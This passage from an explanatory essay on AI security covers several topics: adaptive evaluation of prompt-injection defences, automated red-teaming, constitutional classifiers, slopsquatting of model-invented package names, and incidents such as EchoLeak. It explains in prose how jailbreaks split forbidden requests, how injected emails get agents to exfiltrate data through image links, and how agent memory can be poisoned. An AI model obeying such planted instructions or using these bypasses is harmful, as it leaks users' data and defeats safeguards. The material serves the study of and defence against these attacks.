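The standard template never worked on GPT-5 Mini, with or without a defence, so a static test would have rated all eight rows of the table equally safe. The search found real differences, with success rates from 47% with Spotlighting to 81% with Protect AI's detector. Nasr and colleagues believe a larger budget would bring GPT-5 Mini's rates up to the other models', but did not test this. The search ran only once per task, and its results varied a lot between runs, so small differences in the table mean little.

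### People against automated search

More than 500 people entered the contest, which offered $20,000 in prizes. They could watch the agent reason and act, then revise their attack and try again. The contestants and the search attempted 29 of the same combinations of task, model and defence. At least one person succeeded on each of these, while the search succeeded on 69% of them.

The comparison slightly favours the crowd, because it sets hundreds of people against one run of the search program. Three people attempted all 29. The best of them broke 75%, and the search did better than the other two. Much of the crowd's advantage probably came from its variety.

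Groups of attacking language models also benefit from variety. In *Adaptive Adversaries*, a benchmark presented at the machine learning conference ICML in 2026, Jain, Hartmann and Li had three leading models attack agents in 21 scenarios. Together, the three models found up to 2.4 times as many distinct successful attacks as the best one found alone.

### What a failed attack proves

Static and adaptive tests measure different quantities. Let s_i(a) be 1 if attack a succeeds on task i and 0 if it fails. With n tasks and one fixed attack a₀,

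static success rate = (1/n) Σ s_i(a₀)

adaptive success rate = (1/n) Σ max s_i(a), over the attacks a that the attacker tried on task i

worst-case success rate = (1/n) Σ max s_i(a), over all attacks a that are possible on task i

An attacker can try only some of the possible attacks, so the adaptive rate can never exceed the worst-case rate. A test can therefore prove that a defence is broken, but it cannot prove that it is sound. Nasr and colleagues write that the best result a defence can get is for an evaluation to "fail to prove that the defense is broken."

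A run of failed attacks limits the estimated success rate of future attacks only if they resemble the ones tested. If the true success rate per try is p, the chance that n independent tries all fail is (1 − p)^n. Setting this equal to 5% gives p ≈ 3/n, so a thousand failures in a row would show with 95% confidence that fewer than 0.3% of such attacks work. But attackers can read the same paper and see what failed, so they will look for something different.

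Developers also know which attacks are on a static list, and they adjust their defences until the score is good, sometimes by training on very similar attacks. In most of machine learning, a system that has partly memorised its test can still be of some use, but a security system may only have learned to stop attacks that nobody will use again.

Part of the gap between the two figures in the table comes from repetition, since the standard template got one try at each task and the search got up to 800. This is a fair way to test a defence, because a real attacker can often retry too, but the gap overstates how much cleverer the search's attacks were. When the search succeeded, it usually needed far fewer than 800 tries. Against Gemini 2.5 Pro, half of its successes came within 13 tries when the model had no defence and within 14 when it had Spotlighting.

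*Adaptive Adversaries* gives a cleaner comparison, because the scenarios, attackers and defenders stay the same and only the number of rounds changes. The attacking model receives the defender's response and tries again, while the defender starts each round with no memory of earlier ones. Jain and colleagues found success rates of 0% to 1% in the first round and 8.3% to 19.0% over 15 rounds. The increase may still come as much from repetition as from learning, since 15 independent tries with a 1% chance each would produce at least one success 14% of the time.

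The benchmark also shows that an overall score can hide a weak spot. Attackers beat Claude Opus 4.6 in 8.3% of battles overall and GPT-5.4 in 11.1%, but in one scenario they beat Opus in 60% and GPT-5.4 in 7%. *Adaptive Adversaries* (2026) covers 945 battles, which works out at 15 for each defender in each scenario, so Opus lost about nine battles in that scenario and GPT-5.4 lost one. The models' rankings agreed only weakly across scenarios, with a Kendall's W of 0.21, where 1 is perfect agreement. An attacker who knows which model a company uses can choose a scenario where that model is weak.

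### The same mistake with image classifiers

Carlini had warned AI alignment researchers about this in a talk, *Some Lessons from Adversarial Machine Learning*. About ten years earlier, researchers had discovered that tiny changes to an image could make a classifier badly wrong. In his example, a classifier correctly labels a photograph as a tabby cat with 88% confidence. After a change that people can hardly see, it labels the photograph as guacamole with 99% confidence.

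Such attacks are easy to find, because they use the same calculation as training. Let L(θ, x, y) be the classifier's error on image x with correct label y and weights θ, and let η be a small step size. Training repeatedly adjusts the weights to reduce the error:

θ ← θ − η · ∇_θ L(θ, x, y)

The attacker leaves the weights alone and adjusts the image to increase the error:

x ← x + η · ∇_x L(θ, x, y)

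Researchers repeatedly made mistakes when testing defences, although testing should be simple because anyone who can train a classifier can also attack it. Carlini demonstrated this on a defence that had just appeared at a leading security conference. The classifier was 92% accurate on ordinary images, and when he ran its developers' own attack on a sample of images, accuracy rose to 100%. An attack that raises accuracy is presumably moving in the wrong direction, so Carlini reversed the sign of the attack's step by changing one character in the code, and accuracy fell to 5%.

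He also looked at the best work in the field, in case this example was unrepresentative. Accuracy under strong attack on a standard set of small images had risen steadily until 2020. He had expected it to reach about 90% within a few years, but it levelled off. By his count, researchers had written over nine thousand papers on the problem in ten years.

Carlini expects language models to be worse than image classifiers in one respect, because nobody knows how to test their defences properly. He said he could tell within two days whether a defence for an image classifier worked, but doubted that anyone could do the same for a language model. *Adversarial ML Problems Are Getting Harder to Solve and to Evaluate* (Rando, Zhang and colleagues, 2025), which Carlini co-wrote, gives several reasons. Research on images usually limited the attacker to small changes in each pixel, but an attack on a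 language model can be any text. There is also no formula for an attack program to maximise, because "harmful" lacks the exact meaning that "misclassified" has.

Researchers therefore often use another language model to judge whether an attack worked, and that judge can be wrong or open to attack itself. Rando and colleagues point out that a developer could use the same judge as a filter inside the defence, which would guarantee a perfect score. The judge can also overrate an attack. When Nasr and colleagues attacked StruQ, their attacker learned to raise its score by repeating a string many times, which wasn't evidence of a weakness in the defence. For this reason, they checked their successful attacks by hand.

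There are also reasons to be more optimistic about language models. Carlini granted that text offers far fewer possibilities than the million or so continuous values in an image, which might make defence easier even if testing is harder. Rando and colleagues also mention the view that a model which must never do a certain thing has a simpler job than a classifier, which has to give every answer in the right context. Neither point helps a developer find out today whether a particular defence works.

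### Many attacks, few techniques

Developers often harden an agent by red-teaming it automatically. They run an attack program against it, keep every attack that works and train the agent on the collection. *PIPETTE* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) found a case in which a larger collection produced a weaker agent.

He and colleagues ran two attack programs, PISmith and RL-Hammer, against a small open-weight model, Qwen3-4B, on 560 practice tasks. PISmith succeeded on 69% of the tasks and produced 7,132 working attacks, while RL-Hammer succeeded on 33% and produced 4,282. They trained one copy of the model on each collection of attacks, then tested both copies against three attack methods that neither had been trained on and recorded the worst result for each copy. In those worst results, attacks succeeded on 47.5% of 40 hard tasks against the copy trained on PISmith's larger collection and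 on 27.5% against the other copy.

They repeated the experiment with a second model and a second training method, in which the model learns by copying good behaviour instead of by earning rewards. The table gives the worst result in each case. Its last column shows the results for PIPETTE, their own attack program.

| Model and training method | Trained on RL-Hammer's attacks | Trained on PISmith's attacks | Trained on PIPETTE's attacks |
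|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B, rewards | 27.5% | 47.5% | 20.0% |
| Qwen3-4B, copying | 15.0% | 12.5% | 2.5% |
| Llama-8B, rewards | 25.0% | 27.5% | 10.0% |
| Llama-8B, copying | 15.0% | 20.0% | 5.0% |

PISmith's collection produced the weaker defence in three cases out of four. But there were only 40 tasks, so each accounts for 2.5 percentage points. The largest gap is 19 tasks against 11, according to Zorz's (2026) news report on the study, *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection thousands of times*. The other three gaps are one or two tasks each. This is reasonable evidence that a larger collection may not help, but weak evidence that it generally does harm.

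He and his colleagues think that the attack programs got stuck on a few techniques. A program that earns the same reward for every success gets no extra reward for finding a new technique once it has a good one, such as persuading the agent that the user's task is already finished. Both programs included measures to encourage variety, but these were based only on the text of the attacks. RL-Hammer's developers had reported that the program could satisfy these measures by changing capital letters or adding irrelevant text.

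To test this explanation, they used a language model to describe how each successful attack worked, and condensed the descriptions into a list of 32 recurring techniques. Another model rated, from 0 to 1, how well the list explained attacks from a different source. If a program kept discovering useful techniques, the rating should have risen as its collection grew. RL-Hammer's rating levelled off at about 0.20 on Qwen3-4B and 0.35 on Llama-8B, and PISmith's stopped rising early.

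PIPETTE adds a reward for novelty,

reward = S · (1 − E)

where S is 1 if the attack succeeds and 0 if not, and E is how well the techniques already on the list explain it. The program rebuilds the list every 25 training steps, so a technique soon stops earning this reward. PIPETTE's ratings reached about 0.60 and 0.77. It also collected 8,299 attacks on Qwen3-4B, more than PISmith, and still produced the strongest defence in all four cases. This supports the idea that variety is what matters, although the programs differed in other ways too. Nobody has checked the rating model against human judgement, and He and colleagues do not say that lack of variety was the only cause.

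The full PIPETTE system also trains the agent to check, before each action, whether the text it has just read contains instructions and whether the planned action serves the user's request. The hardened Qwen3-4B completed 65% of ordinary tasks, compared with 62% before hardening, so it was not resisting injection by giving up whenever something looked suspicious.

Static attacks on AgentDojo succeeded less than 0.5% of the time on average against the two small models. He et al. also ran two adaptive searches, with about 250 tries per task, against three models hardened with PIPETTE. The defence cut the stronger search's success rate on the hard tasks from 17.5% to 2.5% on Llama-8B, from 70% to 5% on Qwen3.6-27B and from 92.5% to 10% on GPT-OSS-20B.

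These results are promising, but PIPETTE has not been tested against an attack as strong as the ones that beat the twelve defences. The model that wrote the attacks had only 4 billion parameters, whereas Nasr and colleagues used Gemini 2.5 Pro. The searches used standard prompts with no information about PIPETTE, and no human attackers took part. In the same test, the stronger search succeeded on only 12.5% of tasks against a small model with MetaSecAlign's training, whereas Nasr and colleagues reached 96% against the large version. The small model was harder to hijack to begin with, which explains some of the difference, but the weaker attacker probably explains some of it too.

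### Raising the attacker's costs

A breakable defence may still be worth having if breaking it takes a lot of time or money. Rando and colleagues acknowledge the view that several imperfect layers might provide enough security in practice. Nasr and colleagues accept that filters are useful against unsophisticated attackers, and they did not set out to measure how much time or money an attack takes.

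The paper's data give some idea of how much extra work the defences made for attackers, and for most of the twelve it was little. On Gemini 2.5 Pro, the median number of tries before a success, leaving out tasks where the search failed, rose from 13 with no defence to 20 with MELON and 46 with PIGuard. A program can make a few dozen extra tries for very little money. MELON did better against people in one part of the contest. On Gemini 2.5 Pro with extended reasoning, it cut the share of successful submissions from 11.1% to 0.4%, so a contestant needed almost thirty times as many submissions per success. On GPT-5 with little reasoning, however, the share rose slightly, from 1.9% to 2.4%.

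Anthropic's constitutional classifiers are the best evidence that a defence can make attacks much harder. *Constitutional Classifiers* (Sharma, Tong and colleagues, 2025) describes the first version. Its developers write a "constitution", a list of permitted and forbidden kinds of content. For example, it permits explaining high-school chemistry but forbids helping someone purify restricted chemicals. A language model generates many examples of each kind, along with translations, paraphrases and disguised versions, to train the classifiers. One classifier checks the user's input, and another checks the model's answer as it appears and can stop it partway.

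Anthropic invited 405 people to attack a prototype and offered up to $15,000 for a universal jailbreak, a single method for getting detailed answers to all ten of its questions about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. About 183 people actively took part, spending an estimated 4,720 hours. None of their 113 reports contained a method that got answers to all ten questions with even half the detail an unprotected model would give. But the prototype refused about 44% of ordinary traffic, too much for a commercial product. A later version added only 0.38 percentage points to the refusal rate and 23.7% to the cost of running the model. It blocked 95% of jailbreaks in an automated test, but the contestants never attacked this version.

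Sharma and colleagues concentrate on universal jailbreaks because someone without expertise would need many correct answers in a row to build a weapon. Suppose a project has N steps and the attacker has a 60% chance of getting a detailed answer at each. If the steps are independent, the chance of getting all the answers is 0.6^N, or about 0.6% for ten steps. They offer this kind of model only as an illustration, and it has the same flaw as the seven hidden keys. An attacker who gets one answer has probably found a method that works on other questions too, as a universal jailbreak does.

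Cunningham, Wei and colleagues (2026) report in *Constitutional Classifiers++* that attackers beat the earlier design in further testing. Some split a forbidden request into harmless-looking pieces and scattered them through a longer text. Others had the model disguise its answer so that it made sense only alongside the question. A classifier that reads only the input or only the output can miss both attacks, so the team built one that reads the whole exchange. They later added a classifier that uses less compute to screen every exchange and pass on only the suspicious ones for further checking.

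In the final version, the first check is a simple formula applied to the model's own internal activations, which takes almost no compute. It sends about 5.5% of traffic to a larger classifier, and the system then combines the two scores. The combination works well because the two checks' errors were less correlated than those of two ordinary classifiers, so the second layer adds more than another of the same kind would.

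The next table compares the four versions. A serious break is an attack that got the model to answer more than five of eight forbidden questions with at least half the detail an unprotected model would give, and a universal break got it to answer all eight.

| Version | Attempts | Serious breaks | Universal breaks | Refusals in ordinary traffic | Computing cost (earlier design = 100) |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
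| Earlier design | 695,000 | 13 | 4 | 0.073% | 100 |
| Whole exchange | 226,000 | 2 | 1 | 0.038% | 150 |
| Two stages | 569,000 | 5 | 0 | 0.036% | 27.8 |
| Final version | 198,000 | 1 | 0 | 0.050% | 3.5 |

Attackers spent an estimated 1,736 hours on the final version and found one serious break, which took 30 hours to find. Universal breaks of the earlier design had taken an average of 27 hours. Getting past the classifiers can also make the model's answers worse. Cunningham and colleagues tested two methods of doing so on a set of difficult science questions, and Claude Opus 4's score fell from 74% to 32% with one and 49% with the other. They warn that attackers could probably find methods that reduce the quality of the answers less.

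The reductions in refusals and compute use are large and well measured. The gain in security is harder to judge because there were so few breaks. At the earlier design's rate, 198,000 attempts would produce 3.7 serious breaks on average, and one or none about 12% of the time. Despite the zero in the two-stage row, expert attackers outside the contest found universal jailbreaks for that version, using automated tools and considerable effort.

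The success of these classifiers does not carry over easily to prompt injection. They guard a narrow range of topics and can refuse, whereas an agent that finds planted instructions in an email still has to use the rest of the email. A thief who wants one password or one bank transfer also needs an attack to work only once, while someone trying to make a weapon needs a method that works many times. Filters, like patches, do not protect copies of a model that people have downloaded.

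Cunningham and colleagues note that attackers typically find ways round defences that used to work. They suggest training the guarded model itself to resist attempts at disguise, or using automated red-teaming to produce better training data for the classifiers. The more harm a model could do, the more protection its filter has to give, so a delay of thirty hours might be enough for one model but far too little for a more dangerous one. Developers who rely on slowing attackers down should therefore publish how long skilled attackers who knew the defence's design took to break it, and repeat the test whenever attackers get better tools.

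## Software packages that models invent and attackers register

Coding models sometimes recommend software packages that do not exist, and anyone can then publish malicious software under the invented name. Attackers can exploit this without contacting the victim or the victim's model, whereas beating KataGo or a language model's filter requires sending it input.

### How an invented name becomes an attack

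Programmers often reuse packages, which are bundles of code that other people have published. They download them from public catalogues called registries. The main ones are PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript. The command "pip install", followed by a name, fetches whatever PyPI holds under exactly that name. Churilov (2026) points out in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* that anyone with an email address can publish on either registry, and that neither reviews a newcomer's first upload. A package can run code on the user's machine while it installs, or later when a program loads it.

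A model without a lookup tool builds package names piece by piece from patterns in its training data, so it can produce a plausible invented name as easily as a real one. One such name was react-codeshift, which the programming site DZone describes as a mash-up of two real packages, jscodeshift and react-codemod. Errors also likely arise because many packages have one name for installing and another for use inside a program. Churilov suggests that several companies' models learned the same wrong names from tutorials that mix the two up.

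The attacker asks a model many programming questions, notes which of the packages it names are missing from the registry, and publishes malware under those names. Later, a developer asks a similar question, gets one of the names and installs the package. Churilov's survey of about 200,000 answers cost roughly $1,160 in model fees, and registering a name is free. According to Trend Micro's *Slopsquatting*, Seth Larson coined the term "slopsquatting" for this attack as a play on "typosquatting", where attackers register likely misspellings of real names.

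### Why recurrence matters more than the error rate

*We Have a Package for You!* (Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues, 2024), presented at the USENIX Security conference in 2025, was the first large study of package names invented by models. The team had 16 models write 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code, then compared the packages the code named with the registries' lists. Of 2.23 million package references, 19.7% were to packages that did not exist. The average rate was 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open-source ones. Only 13.4% of the names invented for Python were within two characters of a real one, so most were not simple misspellings.

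These rates give the average number of mistakes, but an attacker also needs to know which name to register. Let r_j be the chance that an answer contains the invented name j, and suppose for simplicity that no answer contains more than one. Then

share of answers with an invented name = Σ r_j, summed over all invented names

developers who receive the attacker's name = q · Σ r_j, summed over the names the attacker registered

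where q is the number of developers who ask. A model that invents a name in 20% of its answers, but never the same name twice, gives the attacker nothing to register in advance. If another model invents a name in only 2% of answers, but always the same one, then 200 out of 10,000 developers will receive the attacker's package.

Real models repeat some invented names but not others. Spracklen and colleagues took 500 prompts that had produced an invented name and ran each ten more times. The same name appeared all ten times in 43% of cases and never in 39%. A developer would word the question differently, and so would probably see the name less often than in these tests.

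Churilov's data give a better idea of how often invented names recur across different questions. In April 2026, Churilov gave nearly 40,000 of Spracklen and colleagues' prompts to each of five models: Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5.4-mini, Gemini 2.5 Pro and DeepSeek V3.2. Depending on the model, between 3.6% and 5.0% of the packages mentioned did not exist. The best model in 2024 had scored 3.59%, so the leading models had barely improved, although DeepSeek's open-weight model had caught up with the commercial ones. The comparison with 2024 is rough because Spracklen and colleagues also asked each model to list the packages its code needed, while Churilov took names only from the code and the install commands.

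The five models had 104 invented names in common. These were under 5% of the 2,282 different names in the data but made up 42% of the 6,363 mentions of invented packages. An attacker who registered them could therefore reach users of several companies' models at once. Some are unavailable because the registries block them or reserve them for particular organisations. Earlier versions of Churilov's paper gave 127 shared names and higher error rates, partly because they counted some correct code as wrong.

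### Demonstrations and real attacks

Researchers have shown that people and programs do install packages with invented names. Spracklen and colleagues cite a test by the security researcher Lanyado, who published a package under such a name and found that developers downloaded it and built it into other software. On 14 January 2026, Charlie Eriksen of the security company Aikido registered the name react-codeshift. Eriksen reports in *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands* that 237 code repositories already contained instructions telling AI agents to install it. People had copied the instructions from one another, and someone had translated them into Japanese, so a model may have invented the name only once. The empty package was soon getting a couple of downloads a day, which Aikido attributes to agents following the instructions.

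Kovacs (2026), in *'HalluSquatting' Turns AI Hallucinations Into Botnet Delivery Mechanism*, reports a related demonstration in which researchers got popular AI assistants to run their code. According to the French news article *HalluSquatting*, the demonstration used invented names of code repositories instead of packages.

Actual attacks are harder to confirm because a malicious package's name rarely shows why the attacker chose it. In October 2025, Koi Security described PhantomRaven, a set of 126 npm packages that had been downloaded more than 86,000 times and contained code that collected developers' access credentials. Koi said models had invented the names, such as unused-imports for the real package eslint-plugin-unused-imports. But Koi published no model output containing these names, and a person could easily shorten the real name in the same way. Endor Labs found 88 more packages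 from the campaign. After an exchange with the packages' author, it softened its account, noting that no credentials appeared to have been taken.

Researchers' packages are often mistaken for malicious ones. OpenSourceMalware, a group that tracks malicious packages, reports that 25% to 41% of the packages added to a public malware database between October 2024 and January 2025 came from researchers looking for bug bounties.

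In August 2026, someone flooded npm with hundreds of packages that installed malware. The headline of OpenSourceMalware's *Russian AI Slopsquatting Publishes 700+ Malicious NPM Packages* attributes the attack to slopsquatting, but the article says the names may have been random. Sonatype's *'Flooding Dropper' Campaign Hits npm With Nearly 850 Malicious Packages* found that many of the names combined stock terms such as "bigops" and "bnpl" with other words, which suggests they came from a name generator rather than a list of names that models had invented.

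*Nearly one in five packages an AI names do not exist* (Churchill, 2026) reports, second-hand, a near miss that is the closest thing to a confirmed attack. A coding agent recommended an invented package to an engineer at the software company Softjourn, and an attacker had already registered the name and filled the package with malware. Softjourn requires staff to check such recommendations by hand. The engineer saw that the package was a few days old and had hardly any downloads, and did not install it.

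Churilov found that people had registered 25 of the 2,282 names within about six months. One of the 25 contained malware, which npm removed, and two were empty. Churilov did not inspect the contents of the other 22, so some may belong to researchers or to developers who chose the same name by chance. The list of 104 shared names had been public by mistake for most of that time, but people registered only one of them, about the same 1% rate as for the unpublished names. The sample was too small to rule out a moderate effect from publishing the list. The models also suggested at least 23 names that had previously belonged to malware, though the people who published the malware may have chosen those names for other reasons.

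Malware exists under package names that models suggest, but none of these accounts documents a theft in which the victim installed the malware because a model suggested it.

### Harmless failures

Until someone registers an invented name, the mistake wastes a minute of the developer's time. The install command returns an error and the developer looks for another package. In *npx Confusion*, Eriksen describes this happening in July 2025 with a name from a project's own documentation. The command failed because the package did not exist. If a stranger had registered the name, Eriksen would have seen a prompt to proceed, with no sign of anything wrong, and would have pressed "y".

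*The Security Mindset and "Harmless Failures"*, a post on the blog of Princeton University's technology policy centre (CITP), calls such cases harmless failures, meaning that an adversary can cause an odd result that does no direct damage. The post's main example is donotreply.com, the domain that companies in Yudkowsky's example used without owning it. The man who registered it received people's replies, along with the bounce messages that mail servers send when an address is wrong. Some bounce messages included the original email, and the contents of these emails included information about military bases in Iraq.

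Like Yudkowsky, the Princeton post says the companies should have avoided the domain without first working out what harm could follow. It argues that looking for the harm protects only a defender clever enough to find it, and that some attacker will be cleverer. Attackers can also combine several harmless failures into a harmful one.

The history of coding models supports this advice. Spracklen and colleagues note that an early assessment, from 2021, rated the risk of models suggesting malicious packages as low and did not explicitly consider invented names. Proving the danger then would have required foreseeing that the names recur, that attackers could easily collect them, and that agents would one day install packages themselves, but someone who disliked installing software from unknown publishers would have had reason for caution without foreseeing any of this.

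But fixing every harmless failure takes time, and many never lead to trouble, as the Princeton post acknowledges. The email problem took almost no effort to fix. A company could use its own domain or one of the names that RFC 2606, an internet standard, reserves so that nobody can register them. One reader commented on how few people knew of the standard. Fixing the problem for packages takes more effort.

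### Comparing the remedies

Developers who install what a model recommends assume that each name leads either to the right package or to nothing. One response is to make the model invent fewer names. Spracklen and colleagues tried this on two open models by adding relevant real packages to the prompt, asking the model to check its own answer, and training it further (fine-tuning) on examples without invented names. The table shows the share of packages that were still invented.

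| Method | DeepSeek Coder 6.7B | CodeLlama 7B |
|---|---|---|
| None | 16.1% | 26.3% |
| Real packages in the prompt | 12.2% | 13.4% |
| Self-checking | 13.0% | 25.5% |
| Fine-tuning | 2.7% | 10.3% |
| All three | 2.4% | 9.3% |

Fine-tuning worked best, but it cut DeepSeek's score on a standard coding test from 51.4% to 25.3%. Adding real packages to the prompt is also unreliable. *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (Djire, Barr and colleagues, 2026) tested eight small models in four programming languages and found that this helped in 18 of the 32 combinations. When the prompts contained fake package names, error rates rose by up to 45 percentage points. Lower error rates protect users because fewer of them receive a fake name, but an attacker needs only a few fake names that models repeatedly invent.

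Checking that a package exists before installing it, another common suggestion, does almost nothing against slopsquatting. If nobody has registered the name, the installation would have failed anyway, and if an attacker has registered it, the check passes. Schipper (2026), in *Slopsquatting*, looked up four names that a recent paper had given as examples of model inventions, and all four existed on PyPI. One was tabula, which a model may suggest for extracting tables from PDF files. That package formats text tables and was last released in 2012, while the developer wants tabula-py.

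The same problem can affect more sophisticated tools. *PackMonitor* (2026) proposes blocking invented package names while the model is writing. Such a tool needs a list of real names, and attackers can add to that list if it comes from an open registry.

Checking who published a package, as Aikido recommends, is much better than checking that it exists. Such a check protected the engineer at Softjourn, but it depends on someone looking carefully every time. Popularity is also a poor guide to safety. The package events-channel, OpenSourceMalware's example of an invented name that attackers had exploited, had 168,000 downloads and was still on npm after people had reported it.

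With an approved list, the company's computers install only packages that someone has reviewed. If a model invents a package name that is not on the list, the installation fails whether or not an attacker has registered the name. Of these remedies, only the approved list means the company no longer has to assume that the model is right or that the name is unclaimed.

The list works only if the reviewers judged each package correctly. It should also name versions, because a later version of an approved package could be malicious. The install tool must also have no other source. Sonatype's *Inside a 176-Package npm Campaign Built to Beat Your Internal Dependencies* describes attackers who try to guess the names of companies' private packages and publish similar ones on npm, many with the version number 99.99.99. A tool that searches both npm and the company's private registry and picks the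 highest version will install the attacker's package. PhantomRaven's packages looked empty on npm but made the installer fetch more code from the attacker's own server. A list that covers only npm names would not stop this.

Spracklen and colleagues call a curated list "blunt and reactive" because someone has to keep checking and updating it. Churilov counts about 857,000 packages on PyPI, so even a list of 10,000 would leave out almost 99% of them. A developer who needs one of the others has to wait for a review, and an agent working overnight has to stop or find another way. The restriction most hinders people who try out new tools and has little effect on a team that uses the same few hundred packages every year.

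Spracklen and colleagues do not measure this drawback, but one of their findings suggests it may be tolerable. The models that invented the fewest packages drew on a smaller set of well-known ones and also scored highest on code quality.

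## Agents that obey instructions hidden in what they read

Slopsquatting depends on a model making a mistake that an attacker has predicted. In prompt injection, the attacker causes the mistake by writing instructions into an email, web page or file that an agent will read. The agent may then follow those instructions, using its user's access to mail, files and money.

### From an incoming email to a harmful action

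Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 illustrates the attack with an email whose hidden text tells an AI assistant to forward the last month of internal messages to an outside address. The user only has to make an ordinary request:

1. The program that runs the assistant gives the model its standing instructions, which describe the job and list the tools it may use, such as searching mail and sending mail.
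2. The user asks for a summary of the inbox.
3. The model answers with a tool call, a short piece of text that names a tool and what to do with it. The program runs the search and gets the messages, including the attacker's.
4. The program adds the messages to the text so far and gives all of it to the model.
5. If the attack works, the model writes another tool call, which forwards the internal messages to the attacker. The program runs this one too, because nothing in a tool call shows whose words led to it.
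6. The model writes the summary. The user sees only this final answer and may never learn that the assistant did anything else.

The attack takes hold at the fourth step. A language model writes one token (a word or piece of a word) at a time, using the probabilities

P(next token | standing instructions, user's request, retrieved emails)

The user's words and the text of any email the agent reads reach the model as a single sequence of tokens. Developers put markers between the parts and train the model to give the user's words priority over an email's. But the markers are tokens too, and the priority is only a learned tendency, which a well-crafted email can overcome. The attacker doesn't need to pick a victim. Anthropic points out that the same email, sent to a thousand inboxes, compromises every agent that summarises it.

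Security engineers call a program in the assistant's position a confused deputy. Someone who lacks the program's authority tricks it into using that authority for them. Norm Hardy named the problem in a 1988 paper, *The Confused Deputy*, about a compiler that let users choose a file for its debugging output. The compiler also had permission to write in the system directory that held the billing records. A user gave the name of the billing file, and the compiler overwrote it. The operating system allowed this because it checked whether the compiler could write there. Similarly, the assistant's forwarding request reaches the mail server as a valid request from the user's own account.

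### Why the cure for SQL injection does not carry over

Web developers had a similar problem with SQL, the language in which programs give commands to databases. A careless website builds a command by pasting in whatever a visitor typed, so a visitor who types some SQL can change what the command does. The fix is a parameterised query, in which the program sends the database a command with a blank in it and sends the value for the blank separately. The database treats the value only as data, so nothing a visitor types can become a command. Like hashing passwords, this removes an assumption, in this case that the website can recognise dangerous text.

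In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) in December 2025, David C warns security staff not to expect a cure for prompt injection like the one for SQL injection. A database engine handles commands and data differently, so developers can keep the two separate. A language model only predicts the next token, so developers have no equivalent way to separate them. Detectors, special markers and training to ignore instructions in data are all attempts to add a distinction that the model lacks, and Nasr and colleagues broke defences of all these kinds. David C therefore thinks prompt injection may never be fully preventable in the way SQL injection is.

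Better markers would not solve another difficulty, which is that people often want an agent to follow instructions in what it reads. If a user says "deal with whatever Priya asks for in her last email", Priya's email is both data and instructions. A model that could identify the source of every word would still have to decide how far Priya's authority went, and what to do if she asked for the company's bank details.

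David C calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy". Programmers can fix Hardy's compiler, for example by making it check whether the user may write to the file. He believes the corresponding flaw in a language model can't be fixed, so he advises builders to reduce the chance of an attack and the damage it can do. If they can't tolerate the remaining risk, he suggests the task may not suit a language model. This is unusual for official advice, since most security guidance assumes the product will be built.

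He advises developers to assume that an injection can do whatever an attacker could do with direct access to the agent's tools, and to limit the agent's actions with ordinary code that does not rely on a model. Marking external text as data is still worthwhile because it makes attacks harder. Blocking known phrases is much less useful because an attacker can keep rewording an instruction. He also recommends logging failed tool calls, since attackers usually have to refine an attack and their early failures may reveal it.

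SQL injection was rare by the time David C wrote, but only after a decade of breaches caused by developers putting unprotected databases behind websites. He fears that companies are repeating this mistake with language models. He is pessimistic about relying on current models to police themselves, but that doesn't rule out systems such as CaMeL, in which ordinary code keeps control and data apart.

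### EchoLeak and the assumptions behind it

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers questions about a user's work by searching their emails, documents and chats. In January 2025, the company Aim Security found that an outsider could steal information from it by sending the user one email. Aim named the flaw EchoLeak, reported it to Microsoft and kept the details private until June, according to SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025). Microsoft rated it critical and fixed it on its own servers in May, as Information Security Buzz reported, so customers did not have to install anything. RedGem's *Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Exposes Microsoft 365 Copilot Data Without User Interaction* gives it a severity score of 9.3 out of 10 and says there was no evidence that criminals had used it.

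The email could sit in the inbox until the user asked Copilot a question it seemed relevant to. Copilot then retrieved it along with internal material and followed the email's planted instructions to put sensitive details from that material into a web address in its answer. Anyone who runs a web server can read the addresses that browsers request from it, so the data escaped as soon as the user's browser requested that address. The usual form of this attack, which the developer Simon Willison (2025) says had already appeared in a dozen products, requires the victim to click a link, but EchoLeak did not.

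Reddy and Gujral, in *EchoLeak*, describe the attack as a chain of bypassed protections. Set out as a safety story, the protections rested on these assumptions:

| Assumption | How it failed |
|---|---|
| Copilot treats a stranger's email only as material for an answer | It followed instructions in the email |
| Microsoft's classifier recognises planted instructions | The email got past it |
| Copilot removes outside links from its answers | It missed links in a less common notation |
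| Data can leave only if the user clicks something | The browser loaded an image by itself |
| The browser loads images only from approved sites, which are safe | An approved Microsoft Teams service passed the request on |

These protections were better than the seven hidden keys because they were of different kinds, and the attacker had to find a way past each one. Repairing any of the last four would have stopped this email. But the first assumption would still have been false, and the next attacker could have looked for another classifier mistake and another way to send data out. Aim called the underlying fault an "LLM Scope Violation", meaning that a model leaks information beyond its intended context. A designer could have avoided relying on the first assumption by keeping strangers' emails separate from internal documents whenever Copilot's answer could trigger a network request.

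### Attacks in 2026

In *AI agent security*, Constantin (2026) counts four research teams that broke AI agents in about ten days in July 2026. Their targets included a browser assistant and an agent's memory.

Manifold Security found that any other extension in the same browser could make Anthropic's browser assistant, Claude for Chrome, read the user's Gmail, Google Docs and Calendar. Claude's extension starts one of nine built-in tasks when the user clicks, but it did not check that a person had made the click, and another extension could fake a click with six lines of code. Manifold rated the flaw as high severity, or critical if the user had switched on "Act without asking", because Claude then read the data silently.

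Constantin sees the same flaw behind all four attacks, but they do not all need the same fix. The Chrome attack did not require fooling the model. The extension was a classic confused deputy, like Hardy's compiler, and ordinary code can fix it because browsers label clicks generated by web scripts. Poisoned memory is harder to fix. An agent with a memory saves notes for later conversations, and if an attacker gets an instruction into those notes, the agent may read it weeks later as part of its own records, with no sign that it came from an attacker.

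*Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) reported in August that criminals were developing tools to plant instructions for AI agents. This is evidence of intent more than of successful thefts, but such tools would let less skilled criminals try.

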